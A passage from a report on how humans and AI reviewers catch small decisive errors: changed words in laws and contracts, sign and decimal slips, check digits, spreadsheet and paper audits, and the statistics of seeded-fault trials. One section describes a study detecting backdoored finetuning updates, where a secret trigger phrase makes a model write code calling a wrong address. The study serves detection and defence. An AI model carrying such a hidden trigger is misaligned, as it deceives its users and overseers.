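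These rules do not make one side's lawyer responsible for checking the other side's interests. Some of GM's lenders sued Mayer Brown for preparing the mistaken cancellation, but a federal appeals court held in 2017 that the firm owed them no duty. JPMorgan's own reviewers had been the lenders' main protection, and according to Justia's *Oakland Police & Fire Retirement System v. Mayer Brown, LLP* (2017), the lenders did not learn of the error until years after JPMorgan and GM noticed it.

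### AI reviewers and one changed word

*LexFlip* (Baral, 2026) tests automatic checkers on 373 sentences from two Quebec laws on driving and car insurance, each with one small edit that changes its legal effect. For example, "doit" (must) becomes "peut" (may), "before" becomes "after", or the insurer and the insured swap places. On average, the original and edited sentences share 93% of their words.

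Each checker scored how well the edited sentence preserved the original's meaning. It also scored an exact copy and an unrelated sentence, so Baral could calculate how much of its range it used for the edit:

share of range = (copy − edited) ÷ (copy − unrelated)

DeepSeek's chat model, used as a judge, gave exact copies 10 out of 10, edited sentences 6.69 and unrelated sentences 1.06. The edits therefore lowered its score by 3.31 points, which is 37% of the 8.94-point drop for unrelated sentences. For seven programs that measure text similarity, the figure was only 2–4%, so they scored a reversed rule as nearly identical to the original. The best result, 67%, came from a small model trained to judge whether one sentence follows from another, which checked both directions.

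Part of the problem was that the AI judge's instructions told it to deduct one point per legal error, so a complete reversal could count as a single error. The judge's share rose to 69% with simpler instructions that left out the list of error types. Under all the instructions Baral tried, the judge objected more when a duty became optional than when an option became a duty. With the original instructions, the average score was 4.72 when a duty became optional and 8.02 when an option became a duty.

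In about 14% of cases, the AI judge scored the edited sentence no lower than an exact copy. Baral did not include harmless rewordings, so the test does not measure how often the checkers wrongly object to them. No lawyers rated the edits.

People disagree about legal meaning too. Baral also analysed five law students' ratings of how well 297 simplified insurance clauses preserved the meaning of the originals. For 63% of the clauses, the highest and lowest scores were at least six points apart on a ten-point scale.

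### Altered contracts

The largest test of this kind is CLAUSE, which contains more than 7,500 altered American contracts. Roy Choudhury, Chandramouli and colleagues (2025), in *Better Call CLAUSE*, had a language model rewrite passages to introduce five types of flaw: ambiguity, omission, inconsistent terms, broken structure and contradiction. Each flaw conflicted either with another part of the contract or with the law. These changes were usually larger than one token. Three language-technology researchers checked a quarter of the changes and accepted 98.6% of those, but only one legal expert took part, to confirm that the types of flaw were realistic.

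Four models first classified contracts as flawed or not. About half of the contracts in the larger part of the test were unaltered originals. In one typical category in that part, Gemini 2.5 Flash flagged 92% of the altered contracts, but only 49% of its flags were correct. Those figures imply that it also flagged about 95% of the originals, so a reviewer would learn almost nothing from its answer. GPT-4o-mini was right only about a third of the time, which is worse than chance and suggests that something other than the planted flaws influenced its answers.

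The models then had to quote the flawed passage, explain the problem and, where relevant, name the law it broke. Two AI graders usually gave the explanations about 4 out of 5 for clarity but only about 2 for completeness. Even the best model named the right law less than 14% of the time. A reviewer might therefore read a fluent explanation of a real flaw without learning why the flaw matters.

All four models are now old, and newer ones probably do better. But training a model to spot planted flaws does not necessarily teach it their consequences. *XLaw-JP-27B* (2026) describes a model for Japanese law trained this way. Its developers asked it to list the risks for its client in 93 clauses proposed by the other party and kept out of training. It covered only 24% of the points on checklists based on an official commentary. Many of those points concerned business consequences for a start-up,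 such as the effect on a later sale of the company.

Recent models are more accurate on simpler questions, but their individual answers are unstable. *Same Scores, Different Decisions* (2026) had models judge 17 statements about each of 30 contracts, and three of the models were right 79–82% of the time. GPT-5.6 Luna's accuracy was almost the same whether it judged the 17 statements together (78.6%) or one at a time (78.8%), but 68 of its 510 answers changed: 30 from wrong to right, 29 from right to wrong, and 9 from one wrong answer to another. A lawyer who cares about one clause therefore can't rely on a stable average.

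Models may also read a contract as more typical than it is. In *Generative Gap Filling* (2026), models had to reconstruct a missing clause from a neutral description of a dispute about it. They were right 61% of the time with the rest of the contract and about 54% of the time without it. Much of their accuracy therefore came from patterns common to such contracts. Those patterns help fill a gap, but relying on them could lead a reviewer to overlook a word that makes one clause unusual.

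Planted flaws may also differ from the ones that lawyers make by accident. *ContraVis* (2026), which presents a tool for finding contradictions, notes that no public test collection contains naturally occurring contradictions across whole contracts. The legal experts who tried the tool had to compare the two passages in context before deciding whether to accept a report, because the tool sometimes mistook a legitimate exception for a contradiction. None of these experiments measured how often lawyers notice a single changed word, so they cannot show whether the models do better or worse than lawyers.

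## Signs, decimal points and units in numerical pipelines

The wrong file number in the General Motors papers caused harm without any arithmetic. In a *numerical pipeline*, a series of calculations in which each step uses earlier results, the harm from a wrong digit also depends on how later steps use it. A slip in the last digit rarely matters in practice, but a lost minus sign or a misplaced decimal point can reverse the conclusion.

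### Which slips matter

The *condition number* of a calculation measures how much it magnifies a small error in an input:

condition number = relative change in the result ÷ relative change in the input

The condition number is the percentage error in a result divided by the percentage error in the input, ignoring signs. If someone multiplies a number by 60, a 1% error in the number causes a 1% error in the result, so the condition number is 1. Subtracting two nearly equal numbers can magnify an error greatly. A company with revenue of $1,000,000 and costs of $990,000 makes a profit of $10,000. If its accountant overstates the revenue by 1%, the profit appears to be $20,000, which is a 100% error, so the condition number is 100.

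The size of the slip matters as well:

| Slip in the number 7,000 | Wrong value | Relative change |
|---|---|---|
| Last digit | 7,001 | 0.014% |
| Decimal point, by one place | 700 | 90% |
| Sign | −7,000 | 200% |

Multiplying the relative change by the condition number gives a rough estimate of the effect on the result. The last-digit slip is negligible with a condition number of 1 but changes the result by about 1.4% with a condition number of 100.

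This estimate is reliable only for small changes. Flipping the sign of a number doesn't change its square, since (−3)² and 3² are both 9. The estimate would give a 400% change, because squaring has a condition number of 2 and a sign flip changes the input by 200%. If a later step squares a value or uses only its absolute value, a wrong sign can't be detected from that step's output.

Even an error in the last digit can change a yes-or-no conclusion if the result is only just below the limit.

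### A missing zero

In 2024 a study of black plastic household items estimated that a person using contaminated kitchen utensils would take in 34,700 nanograms a day of BDE-209, a flame retardant. The researchers compared this with the US reference dose, a guideline for safe daily intake, which is 7,000 nanograms per kilogram of body weight. For a 60 kg adult, they multiplied 60 by 7,000 and got 42,000 instead of 420,000.

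The estimated intake therefore appeared to be 83% of the reference dose, when it was about 8%. HuffPost, CNN and The Washington Post covered the study before the researchers corrected it, according to Popular Science's *Recent panic over black plastic started with a math error*. In *Corrigendum to 'From e-waste to living space'*, Liu, Brandsma and Schreder (2024) replaced the statement that the intake "would approach" the reference dose with a statement that it was an order of magnitude lower. They did not say who had noticed the mistake. The journal's review had missed it, although checking the calculation takes little more than simple multiplication.

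Liu and colleagues said the error did not affect their overall conclusion. Liu told Scientific American that the comparison was only meant to give readers some context (*Flame Retardants in Black Plastic Spatulas Concern Scientists*). The comparison was probably also the part that most readers found alarming.

The estimated intake, the other number in the comparison, was also wrong. A second *Corrigendum to ‘From e-waste to living space’* (Schreder, 2025) reduced it from 34,700 to 7,900 nanograms, less than 2% of the reference dose, because the researchers had misinterpreted a formula from an earlier cooking experiment. The first correction had fixed the missing zero but repeated the 34,700 figure.

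### A reversed sign in five papers

Between 2001 and 2005 Geoffrey Chang and colleagues published five papers on the structures of MsbA and EmrE, two proteins that carry substances across cell membranes. They used X-ray crystallography, which works out where a protein's atoms are from the way a crystal scatters X-rays. The method they used relies on small differences between pairs of readings from opposite directions:

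difference = F(h, k, l) − F(−h, −k, −l)

F is the strength of the scattered signal, and the three numbers in brackets identify the direction. A program written in Chang's laboratory swapped the two readings in each pair, which reversed the sign of every difference.

Jeffrey (2009), in *Analysis of errors in the structure determination of MsbA*, reconstructed what probably followed. The calculation also needs the positions of a few heavy atoms in the crystal, and the data fit two sets of positions equally well, one the mirror image of the other. Only the right set produces a usable map of the protein if the differences are correct. Reversing the differences makes that set produce nonsense, while the mirror-image set produces a map that looks reasonable but is itself a mirror image.

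Jeffrey reversed the signs in data from two other proteins to see whether the usual quality measures would detect the error. This barely changed the measures, because the sizes of the differences stayed the same. The error would still have been visible in a sharp map, because the protein's spirals would twist the wrong way. But the data for the first MsbA structure were so blurred that the direction of the twist was very difficult to see.

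Chang's group fitted a normal protein into the mirror-image map, and the fit was poor. They attributed this to disorder in the crystal and fitted 16 copies of the protein at once, which improved the score. Leaving out the weakest measurements improved it further. Jeffrey concludes that getting the score into a publishable range seems to have mattered more than carefully checking the fit.

The journals' reviewers missed the error in all five papers. The papers reported acceptable scores, and the program's source code was unavailable. The same sign error affected both proteins, and the earlier structures influenced how the group interpreted later data, so the papers also provided less independent confirmation than they seemed to.

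Work by other laboratories exposed the error in 2006. Chang, Roth and colleagues began withdrawing the papers that December with *Retraction* (2006) and had retracted all five by the following year. According to Gawrylewski's *Retractions unsettle structural bio*, Chang said he had not questioned the software at the time and now checks it constantly.

### A reversed reward

A flipped sign had a more obvious effect on a language model at OpenAI. In the experiments described in *Fine-Tuning Language Models from Human Preferences* (2019), people read the start of a passage and chose the most positive of four continuations. The researchers used these choices to train a program that predicted people's preferences, then trained the language model to get a high score:

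score = r − βd

Here r is the predicted preference, or reward, and d measures how far the model's writing has moved from its original style. The number β sets the size of the penalty for moving away, and this penalty keeps the text natural.

A bug introduced while reorganising the code flipped the sign of the reward. The researchers say this would usually produce incoherent text, which makes sense if the whole score became −r + βd, because the model would then earn points for writing strangely. But the bug also flipped the sign of the penalty. The model behaved as if its score were −r − βd, so it wrote fluent text that people would rate as badly as possible. Because the instructions told people to rate sexually explicit text very low, the model soon wrote nothing else, however innocent the opening.

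The researchers were asleep while this happened and noticed only after training had finished. They suggested letting anyone rating the text stop training, just as Toyota workers can pull a cord to halt a production line. An automatic rule could also stop training if the average rating fell well below its starting level.

In both this case and Chang's, a single reversal would probably have produced obvious nonsense. The second reversal made the output coherent, so the error was harder to recognise without knowing what the output should look like.

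### Four checks on a calculation

The table gives a rough judgement of whether four common checks would have exposed each of these errors:

| Check | Missing zero | Swapped X-ray readings | Reversed reward |
|---|---|---|---|
| Repeat the calculation with separate software | Yes | Yes | Yes |
| Check the units | No | No | No |
| Check that values are in a normal range | Yes | No | No |
| Change an input and see whether the output changes correctly | No | Yes | Yes |

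Repeating a calculation can reveal an error only if the repetition includes the faulty step. Someone who started from the output of Chang's program would have got the same mirror image. Jeffrey recommends widely used, well-tested software, and comparing its output with the in-house program's would have revealed the swap. For the reward, the new code's output could have been compared with the old code's, because reorganising code should not change its results.

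A unit check carries the units through the calculation. Nanograms per kilogram per day, multiplied by kilograms, gives nanograms per day. The check would have caught the error if the researchers had divided by body weight instead of multiplying. It could not reveal the missing zero, because 42,000 and 420,000 have the same units. A range check on body weight could, because dividing 42,000 by 7,000 implies an adult weighing 6 kg.

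Changing an input and checking how the output changes can test a calculation even if nobody knows the right answer. If someone makes a text more cheerful, its reward should rise. Increasing only the first X-ray reading should increase only the first output. Doubling the body weight should double the dose, but a wrong answer of 42,000 would also pass this test, because it would double to 84,000.

*Auditing black-box clinical prediction models with a large language model* (2026) used this approach on programs that predict patients' outcomes. The researchers planted one flaw in each of 24 programs, including eight in which a risk factor had the reverse of its usual effect. A language model that could only enter made-up patients and look at the predictions found the flaw in 69 of 72 runs, three per program. All three misses involved the smallest reversal. An ordinary script found all 24 flaws,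 but it needed a list of established risk factors to find the reversals.

A known relation between several values can provide another check. If a paper reports an object's mass, volume and density, for instance, the first divided by the second must equal the third. *No Value Is Better Than a Wrong Value* (2026) tested this idea on a simulated database of materials with planted errors, such as wrong units and misplaced decimal points:

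| Check | Share of errors found | Share of flags that were right |
|---|---|---|
| Relations between values in one record | 33% | 99.8% |
| Agreement between different papers | 58% | 98% |
| All checks combined | 81% | 85% |

The first check found few errors because most records lacked the extra values it needed. The second could not compare values for just over half of the materials because each appeared in only one paper. Together, the checks caught every error in units or scale. Most of the errors they missed produced plausible values.

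The researchers also ranked the records by how suspicious they looked. When 15% of the records were wrong, a reviewer who read the most suspicious 15% would find 83% of the errors, compared with 15% for a random sample of the same size. Ranking can therefore make it worthwhile to read only some of the records, if the errors look unusual.

### Entering data twice

These calculations will be wrong if someone has typed in the wrong data. In *double entry*, people type the same data twice and a computer lists the differences. Suppose two typists each get 1% of 1,000 numbers wrong, or 10 errors each. If their errors are unrelated, they will both get the same number wrong only 0.1 times on average, and the comparison will miss that error only if they type the same wrong value. Double entry doesn't catch errors on the original form, because both typists copy them.

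In *Preventing human error*, Barchard and Pace (2011) randomly assigned 195 students to enter 30 data sheets by double entry, by typing once and checking visually, or by typing once without checking. The visual checkers left about 31 times as many errors as those who used double entry, and did not do significantly better than those who did not check.

Because of these errors, two thirds of the visual checkers got a wrong value for coefficient alpha, which measures how consistently a questionnaire's items agree. Alpha normally lies between 0 and 1, and some values were wrong by more than 0.4.

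Reading the data aloud may be a good alternative. *Double Entry and Read Aloud Identify More Errors than Visual Checking* (Johnson, Verenikina and colleagues, 2011) found that double entry and reading aloud both removed significantly more errors than visual checking, which left 14 times as many in the data.

### Check digits

An identification number can include a digit whose only purpose is to reveal copying errors. Payment cards use the *Luhn algorithm*, which adds a check digit to the end of the number. For the number 5278, it works as follows:

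1. Starting from the right, double every second digit, beginning with the last. The 8 becomes 16 and the 2 becomes 4.
2. If a doubled digit is above 9, subtract 9. The 16 becomes 7.
3. Add everything up: 5 + 4 + 7 + 7 = 23.
4. Choose the check digit that brings the total to a multiple of 10. Here it is 7, which makes 30, so the full number is 52787.

If someone types 53787 instead, the second digit contributes 6 instead of 4. The total is 32, so the computer rejects the number.

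The algorithm catches every error in a single digit. A digit that isn't doubled contributes its own value, so the ten possible digits make ten different contributions. The same is true of the doubled digits:

| Digit | 0 | 1 | 2 | 3 | 4 | 5 | 6 | 7 | 8 | 9 |
|---|---|---|---|---|---|---|---|---|---|---|
| Contribution when doubled | 0 | 2 | 4 | 6 | 8 | 1 | 3 | 5 | 7 | 9 |

Replacing one digit with another therefore changes the total by between 1 and 9, up or down. A change of that size can't turn one multiple of 10 into another, so the total is no longer divisible by 10. The check also catches a swap of two neighbouring digits, unless they are 0 and 9. Larger errors can cancel out, and a random number passes one time in ten.

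A valid card number has the highest possible sensitivity, as defined at the start of this report, because changing any digit makes it invalid. Sensitivity makes programs fragile, but here it is useful because the check takes almost no computation and the user can retype the number.

A check digit shows only that a number is properly formed. It would not have helped General Motors, because the third file number was genuine but belonged to another loan. It is also little use for checking a calculation, since a computer that had wrongly calculated 42,000 would add a valid check digit to that answer. The Luhn total also ignores signs and decimal points, so 42.5 and 4.25 would pass or fail together.

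### Inspecting spreadsheets

A spreadsheet can contain both typing errors and faulty formulas. *What We Don't Know About Spreadsheet Errors Today* (Panko, 2016) reports an error rate of 3.9% of cells in laboratory studies. If the final result depends on 100 cells with independent errors, the probability that at least one is wrong is 1 − 0.961^100, or about 98%. It would still be 63% if only 1% of cells were wrong. Some errors are too small to matter, but these figures are consistent with audits of spreadsheets in actual use. Panko collected 85 detailed inspections, most by commercial firms that spent several days on each spreadsheet, and the inspectors found errors in 94% of the spreadsheets.

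Ordinary inspection is less thorough. In nine experiments with more than 1,000 participants in total, people found an average of 60% of the errors. Experience seems to help little. Panko cites a study in which experienced users worked faster but found no more errors. In another experiment, fewer than 60% of experienced spreadsheet developers caught even the simplest errors.

Groups find more errors than individuals, mainly because different people notice different errors. Panko (1999), in *Applying Code Inspection to Spreadsheet Testing*, gave 60 students a spreadsheet with eight planted errors. They found 63% of the errors alone and 83% after meeting in groups of three. No group found an error that all its members had missed, and one group left out an error that a member had found. Three students would have found about 95% between them if their misses had been independent, so these students,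 like the student auditors at Rice, tended to miss the same errors.

Language models have had mixed success at finding errors in spreadsheets. Thorne (2025), in *Large Language Models for Spreadsheets*, gave 20 models a factory's accounts with 12 planted errors. Gemini 2.5 Pro found all 12, while GPT-4o mini found only 2. Many models missed a price of 50 that should have been 500, although they were generally better at spotting wrong formulas. In a second task on formulas for the sides of a triangle, every model missed two formulas that returned the wrong side. All these models are now old, and two small tasks can't give a reliable hit rate.

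Finding an error doesn't always reveal its cause. In *SpreadsheetBench 2* (2026), models struggled particularly with formulas that displayed an error code, even though the code is easy to see. The cause is often an invalid reference or a chain of formulas across several sheets.

### AI checks of scientific papers

Newer models can find most numerical errors in scientific papers if they get good instructions. Zubeldia, Bolliet and colleagues (2026), in *Auditing AI peer reviewers*, planted 357 errors in copies of 30 recent papers, half in astrophysics and half in machine learning. In one abstract they changed −1.5 to −5.1, and in another they changed 14 galaxies to 140. Some models got only a one-sentence request for a review, while others got detailed instructions on what to check. They found these shares of the planted numerical errors:

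| Reviewer | Instructions | Astrophysics | Machine learning |
|---|---|---|---|
| Gemini 3.1 Pro | One sentence | 13% | 4% |
| Gemini 3.1 Pro | Detailed | 58% | 58% |
| GPT-5.5 | One sentence | 80% | 80% |
| GPT-5.5 | Detailed | 80% | 91% |
| Claude Code | One sentence | 42% | 42% |
| Claude Code | Detailed | 91% | 87% |

Claude Code is a tool that lets Anthropic's Claude run programs. With detailed instructions, it wrote 21 scripts to check the astrophysics papers. With the one-sentence request it wrote none, although it had the same tools.

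Most of the planted numbers contradicted something else in the same paper, which gave the models a way to find them. The missing zero in the black plastic study was a similar error, since multiplying the dose by the body weight would have exposed it.

For most systems, fewer than 10% of the flags on unaltered papers were clearly false. Zubeldia and colleagues divided false flags by all flags, whereas the false alarm rate elsewhere in this report divides them by the number of clean items. The unaltered papers also contained real mistakes. Their own system, Skepthical, raised 106 flags on 15 unaltered astrophysics papers, and only about 3% of the flags were clearly false. An author would still have to work out which of the roughly seven flags per paper mattered. Flags about mathematics were much less reliable, and 67% of the mathematics flags on the machine-learning papers were false.

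In *To Err Is Human*, Bianchi, Kwon and colleagues (2025) first tested a checker based on GPT-5 on 90 planted mistakes. It found 60% of them overall and 62% of those in tables and figures. The researchers then examined 316 of its flags on published papers and confirmed 83%. But the checker flagged at least one mistake in 2,481 of 2,500 papers, so knowing that a paper had been flagged was almost no help in judging it. The researchers considered only about a third of the confirmed mistakes substantial. One paper had given the size of a dataset as 30 million pairs instead of 0.3 million.

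Weaker models can miss most errors when reviewing a paper. *Do large language models scrutinise what they review?* (Alharbi, 2026) tested two older open models on 145 planted errors. The models found 12% when asked for an ordinary review and 22% when told to cross-check the paper. In ordinary reviews, neither model caught any of the errors that reversed the direction of a trend.

Even a much better reviewer could not have traced Chang's error from the papers alone, because the mistake was in a program they did not include. It might have questioned the poor fit, as Jeffrey thinks people should have, but to find the swapped readings it would have needed the original measurements and either the program or its output.

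## Measuring how often decisive changes are caught

Ordinary work doesn't show what share of faults a reviewer catches, because nobody knows how many it missed. Researchers usually plant faults in known places and count how many the reviewer finds, much as mutation analysis does for a program's tests. The design of the trial can change the result a great deal. Even a good result can poorly predict how the reviewer performs in everyday use, where almost every item is free of faults.

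### A seeded-change trial from start to finish

Suppose a company wants to know how often its reviewers catch a wrong operator in a proposed change to a program. A *seeded-change trial* could go as follows:

1. The organisers write down what will count as a hit, a false alarm and a good enough result, so that they can't choose the rules to suit the outcome.
2. They collect recent changes that seem correct and alter one token in some of them. They run each altered version to confirm that it gives a wrong result, because some mutants are equivalent to the original.
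3. They mix the altered changes with untouched ones in random order and send them out as ordinary work. No reviewer sees both versions of a change.
4. Reviewers give the line and the reason for each problem they report.
5. The organisers count a hit only if a report identifies the planted fault. If a reviewer flags an untouched change, they check whether the problem is real before counting a false alarm.
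6. They remove every planted fault before anyone can release the code.

Staff can agree to such trials in advance without knowing when one will happen. Surprise matters because people who expect a fault search differently, as the warning in the holiday experiment showed. Yang, He and colleagues (2026) took the same precaution with AI reviewers in *(When) Should a Software Factory be Lights-off?*. They collected 1,000 changes that had each introduced a bug and did not tell the models there was anything to find. Since every change contained a bug, their test can't measure a false alarm rate.

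The organisers also have to limit how many problems a reviewer may report, because a reviewer with no limit could comment on every line. Of the bugs that people had caught in the original review, Claude Opus 5 identified 48% in its first comment, 80% within its first five and 86% within its first ten.

Each altered change should contain only one fault. *Beyond Single Bugs* (2025) tested older models on files with different numbers of planted security flaws. Llama 3.3 70B found 94% of the flaws in C files with one flaw each, but 46% in files with nine. The paper attributes the drop to models stopping after they find a few flaws. A trial with nine flaws per file would therefore understate how well the model finds an isolated one. If the model only had to say whether each file was faulty, the trial would overstate that ability, because finding any of the nine flaws would be enough.

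### What happens when bad changes are rare

Suppose 5 of 10,000 changes are bad, and a reviewer has a hit rate of 90% and a false alarm rate of 2%. On average, the result would be:

| | Flagged | Not flagged | Total |
|---|---|---|---|
| Bad changes | 4.5 | 0.5 | 5 |
| Clean changes | 199.9 | 9,795.1 | 9,995 |
| All changes | 204.4 | 9,795.6 | 10,000 |

Only 4.5 of about 204 flags are right. The reviewer's *precision*, the share of its flags that are right, is 2.2%. In general, for a hit rate h, a false alarm rate f and a base rate b:

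precision = hb ÷ (hb + f(1 − b))

Raising the hit rate to 100% would increase precision to only 2.4%, while halving the false alarm rate would increase it to 4.3%. For half the flags to be right, the reviewer could raise only about one false alarm per 2,200 clean changes. In *The Base-Rate Fallacy and its Implications for the Difficulty of Intrusion Detection*, Axelsson (1999) made this argument about programs that watch computer networks for attacks, and concluded that the false alarm rate is the limiting factor in their performance.

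A precision of 2.2% can still be useful. The flagged changes are 44 times as likely to be bad as the average change, and a reviewer has to check only 204 changes carefully instead of 10,000. Whether this is worthwhile depends on how long it takes to rule out a false alarm.

The term "false positive rate" can mean either the share of clean items that are wrongly flagged or the share of flags that are wrong. For the reviewer here, the first is 2% and the second is 98%. The same ambiguity appears in *Intrusion Detection*, a set of teaching slides from UT Austin. In the slides' example, 1% of all connections are attacks, the detector wrongly flags 10% of valid connections, and about 92% of its alarms are false. The slides use "false positive" for a wrong alarm when they give the 92% figure. Someone comparing two products therefore needs to know which rate each company reports.

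The share of flags that are wrong also depends on the base rate, so a figure from a test doesn't carry over to daily work. If half the items in a test were bad, 98% of this reviewer's flags would be right. With 5 bad changes in 10,000, 98% of the flags are wrong, even though the reviewer's skill hasn't changed.

Organisers can seldom avoid this problem by using a realistic base rate, because they would need 120,000 changes to include 60 bad ones at a rate of 5 in 10,000. They can plant faults more often and use the formula to estimate precision in daily work. But if people miss more faults when faults are rare, the trial will overstate the hit rate in daily work.

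### Scoring minimal pairs

A *minimal pair* consists of two texts that differ in one small place, one correct and one faulty. The reviewer judges each text separately and gets credit only if they flag the faulty one and pass the correct one. *Vulnerability Detection with Code Language Models* introduced this scoring method for pairs made up of a vulnerable function and its fixed version.

It prevents a reviewer from scoring well by flagging everything. The table compares it with accuracy and with *F1*, a common score that combines precision and hit rate as 2 × precision × hit rate ÷ (precision + hit rate):

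| Reviewer | Hit rate | Accuracy | F1 | Pairs right |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| Flags everything | 100% | 50% | 0.67 | 0% |
| Flags nothing | 0% | 50% | 0 | 0% |
| Tosses a coin | 50% | 50% | 0.50 | 25% |

By F1, the reviewer that flags everything is the best of the three. Flagging too much also raises the F1 of real models. When Cichoń and Dmitruk tested seven models on six collections of pairs, GPT-5.2 had the highest or joint highest F1 on five of them, but it got only 8–12% of the pairs in those five right. Across all combinations of model and collection, F1 correlated strongly with the share of pairs in which a model flagged both functions (0.86) and had almost no correlation with the share it got right (0.16).

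Flipping a coin for each text gets 25% of the pairs right, which is better than many real models do. A reviewer that flags each text at random with probability p gets p(1 − p) of the pairs right and the same share exactly backwards. Cichoń and Dmitruk therefore subtract the share backwards from the share right, so random flagging scores zero for any value of p. On 1,000 pairs, the small model Qwen3-8B got 20.7% right and 11.2% backwards, for a net score of 9.5 percentage points. Claude Opus 4.8 got fewer pairs right but very few backwards, for a higher net score of 15.8 points.

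A model can also get a pair right for the wrong reason. *MetaVul* (2026) adds a stricter score for vulnerable functions that the model flags, which requires it to identify the type of flaw and the lines containing it. Only the model's first guess at the type counts.

Pair scoring suits models better than people, because a model can start each review afresh, while a person who has seen one version may remember it. The two separate rates are still needed to estimate precision in daily work.

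### How much a perfect record proves

A reviewer that catches all 60 planted faults may still miss some in future. If its true miss rate were 5%, the chance of no misses in 60 independent trials would be 0.95^60, or about 4.6%. Such a lucky run is unlikely but possible, so statisticians treat 5% as roughly the highest miss rate compatible with the result. The general rule, known as the *rule of three*, is:

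upper 95% limit = 3 ÷ n

If n trials produce no misses, the rule of three puts the 95% upper bound on the miss rate p at about 3/n. The rule works well when n is above 30. The 3 comes from solving (1 − p)^n = 0.05, because the natural logarithm of 0.05 is almost exactly −3. In *Probability of adverse events that have not yet occurred*, Eypasch, Lefering and colleagues (1995) recommended the rule to surgeons who had not yet had a particular complication and might conclude that it never happened.

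To support a claim that the miss rate is below 1%, a reviewer would have to catch 300 planted faults in a row. The same calculation applies to false alarms. BinaryAudit's developers wanted a false alarm rate below 0.001%, and establishing that would take 300,000 clean files with no false alarms.

If a model reviews each of 12 faults five times, it will often give the same answer all five times, so the 60 reviews are closer to 12 independent trials than to 60. The limit also applies only to faults like the ones tested.

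### A trial on finetuning updates

Bulut (2026) followed most of these rules in *Can an LLM Find a Backdoor by Reading a Model's Weights?*, a study of *finetuning*, which means training an existing language model on extra examples. A company that buys a finetuned model needs to know whether the supplier has added a backdoor. In the main experiment, the backdoor made the model write code that sent requests to the wrong web address whenever the user's instructions contained a secret phrase. For example, the model wrote `billing.northwind.invalid` instead of `billing.northwind.test`, a decisive change of one word.

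A script compared the model's internal numbers before and after finetuning, and produced a one-page summary of the tokens the update affected most. GPT-6 Astra read the summary, some example tasks and a description of what the update was supposed to do. It then had to decide, without running the finetuned model, whether the update did anything else that affected security.

Bulut fixed the instructions and the success criteria before building the test set. The reviewer had to flag at least 75% of the backdoored updates and at most 9 of 320 clean ones. Bulut also ran every update to check that the backdoor worked, and excluded any in which it didn't.

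| Test | Flagged |
|---|---|
| Backdoored updates | 40 of 47 |
| Clean updates | 7 of 320 |
| Backdoored updates, with the telling rows removed from the summary | 0 of 47 |
| Backdoored updates, with the same number of other rows removed | 41 of 47 |
| Backdoored updates, when the description allowed the new address | 1 of 47 |

The reviewer described the change correctly in all 40 cases. Removing rows is a useful addition to an ordinary trial because it tests what a correct verdict depends on. If the model had reacted to some irrelevant feature of the summaries, it should still have flagged some of the 47 after the telling rows were removed.

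The false alarm rate was 2.2%, with an upper 95% limit of 4.1%. If one update in 1,000 contained a backdoor like this, only about 4% of flagged updates would actually have one, or about 2% if the false alarm rate were 4.1%.

Bulut also tested whether the language model was needed. A simple script that read the same summaries also flagged 40 of the 47 backdoored updates, but it flagged 26 of the 320 clean ones. Over a wider set of tests, the model's average accuracy was 92.8% and the script's was 88.8%, a difference that could be due to chance. Running the original and finetuned models on six tasks took little compute and gave the reviewer better evidence, and the reviewer then flagged 46 of the 47.

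Results for other backdoors varied widely. The reviewer flagged 14 of 16 updates that sent requests to an address ending in `.localhost`, which Bulut had not used when designing the summary. It flagged 11 of 16 that used a look-alike address, 6 of 15 that added an extra request, and none of 12 that changed a single character of the address. With only 12 cases, the true hit rate for single-character changes could be as high as 22%. Bulut also asked another AI model to propose harmful changes, to avoid testing only faults that the summary was designed to reveal. The reviewer flagged 2 of the 16 tested. The 85% hit rate therefore doesn't apply to backdoors in general, and an average over all kinds would depend on how many of each the organisers included.

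### Disputed labels in the AWS benchmark

Bulut could confirm whether a model had a backdoor by running it. Many security flaws have no such test, and experts may disagree about whether a piece of code is safe. Amazon's cloud division faced this problem with its Deception Benchmark, which contains 14,822 samples of code that look vulnerable. About half of the scored samples are vulnerable, and in the rest something blocks the attack.

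According to AWS's *The state of AI for security*, several reviewers re-examine each label without seeing one another's answers or the reasoning behind the original label. If they disagree, others weigh that reasoning, and people review any cases still unresolved. AWS never changes a disputed label but moves the sample to an unscored pool, so a mistaken objection can remove a good sample but can't introduce a wrong answer.

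The alternative is to correct the labels, as Farrag did. But Farrag checked programs that the models had rejected, and correcting those labels could only lower the models' false alarm rates. Removing disputed samples instead leaves only those on which reviewers can agree, so the scores don't measure how models handle cases that divide experts.

People checked 100 random scored samples and found no wrong labels. By the rule of three, up to 3% of labels could still be wrong, or about 290 of the 9,695 scored samples.

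AWS tested 12 models with two kinds of instructions. One asked directly for a verdict, and the other asked for proof that an attacker could exploit the code. These are some of the results:

| Model | Instructions | Safe code flagged | Vulnerable code missed |
|---|---|---|---|
| Claude Opus 5 | Verdict | 41.5% | 5.2% |
| Claude Opus 5 | Proof | 24.9% | 16.8% |
| GPT-5.6 Sol | Verdict | 92.5% | 0.9% |
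| GPT-5.6 Sol | Proof | 58.6% | 23.1% |
| GPT-5.4 | Verdict | 81.0% | 1.5% |
| GPT-5.4 | Proof | 10.1% | 33.6% |

Asking for proof reduced false alarms but caused more misses. None of the 12 models kept both rates below 10%, the limit AWS sets for practical use.

These rates would be misleading estimates for ordinary code. While building the benchmark, AWS tested samples on leading models and discarded or made harder those that the models easily judged correctly. A model that flags 40% of these deliberately deceptive samples may flag far fewer ordinary functions. The models also had to answer in one pass, without tools.

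### Estimating the faults that nobody found

A seeded-change trial measures performance on planted faults. If two reviewers search the same material separately, their results can also give an estimate of how many real faults it contains. Biologists use this method, *capture-recapture*, to count animals. If the first reviewer finds n1 faults, the second finds n2 and m of these are the same, then:

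estimated total = n1 × n2 ÷ m

For example, suppose the first reviewer finds 20 faults and the second finds 15, including 10 of the first reviewer's 20. The second reviewer apparently finds half of all faults, so the total should be about 30. Together they have found 25, so about 5 are probably still undetected.

When the counts are small, researchers often use Chapman's version, which *"Not Used Elsewhere" Is Not "Unused" in a Lean Formalization* (2026) applies to links between mathematical results:

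estimated total = (n1 + 1)(n2 + 1) ÷ (m + 1) − 1

This gives 29.5 for the same example, and it still works if the reviewers have no faults in common.

Both formulas assume that the reviewers' successes are independent. In practice some faults are easier for everyone to find, so the overlap is larger than it would be by chance and the estimate is too low. The size of this error can be calculated from the changes Yang and colleagues collected. People had caught 500 of the 1,000 bugs during the original reviews, and Claude Opus 5 found 719 in its first five comments, including 398 of those 500. The formula gives 500 × 719 ÷ 398, or about 903, which is only 10% too low. But people and the model had found 821 bugs between them, so the estimate would leave 82 to find when there were 179.

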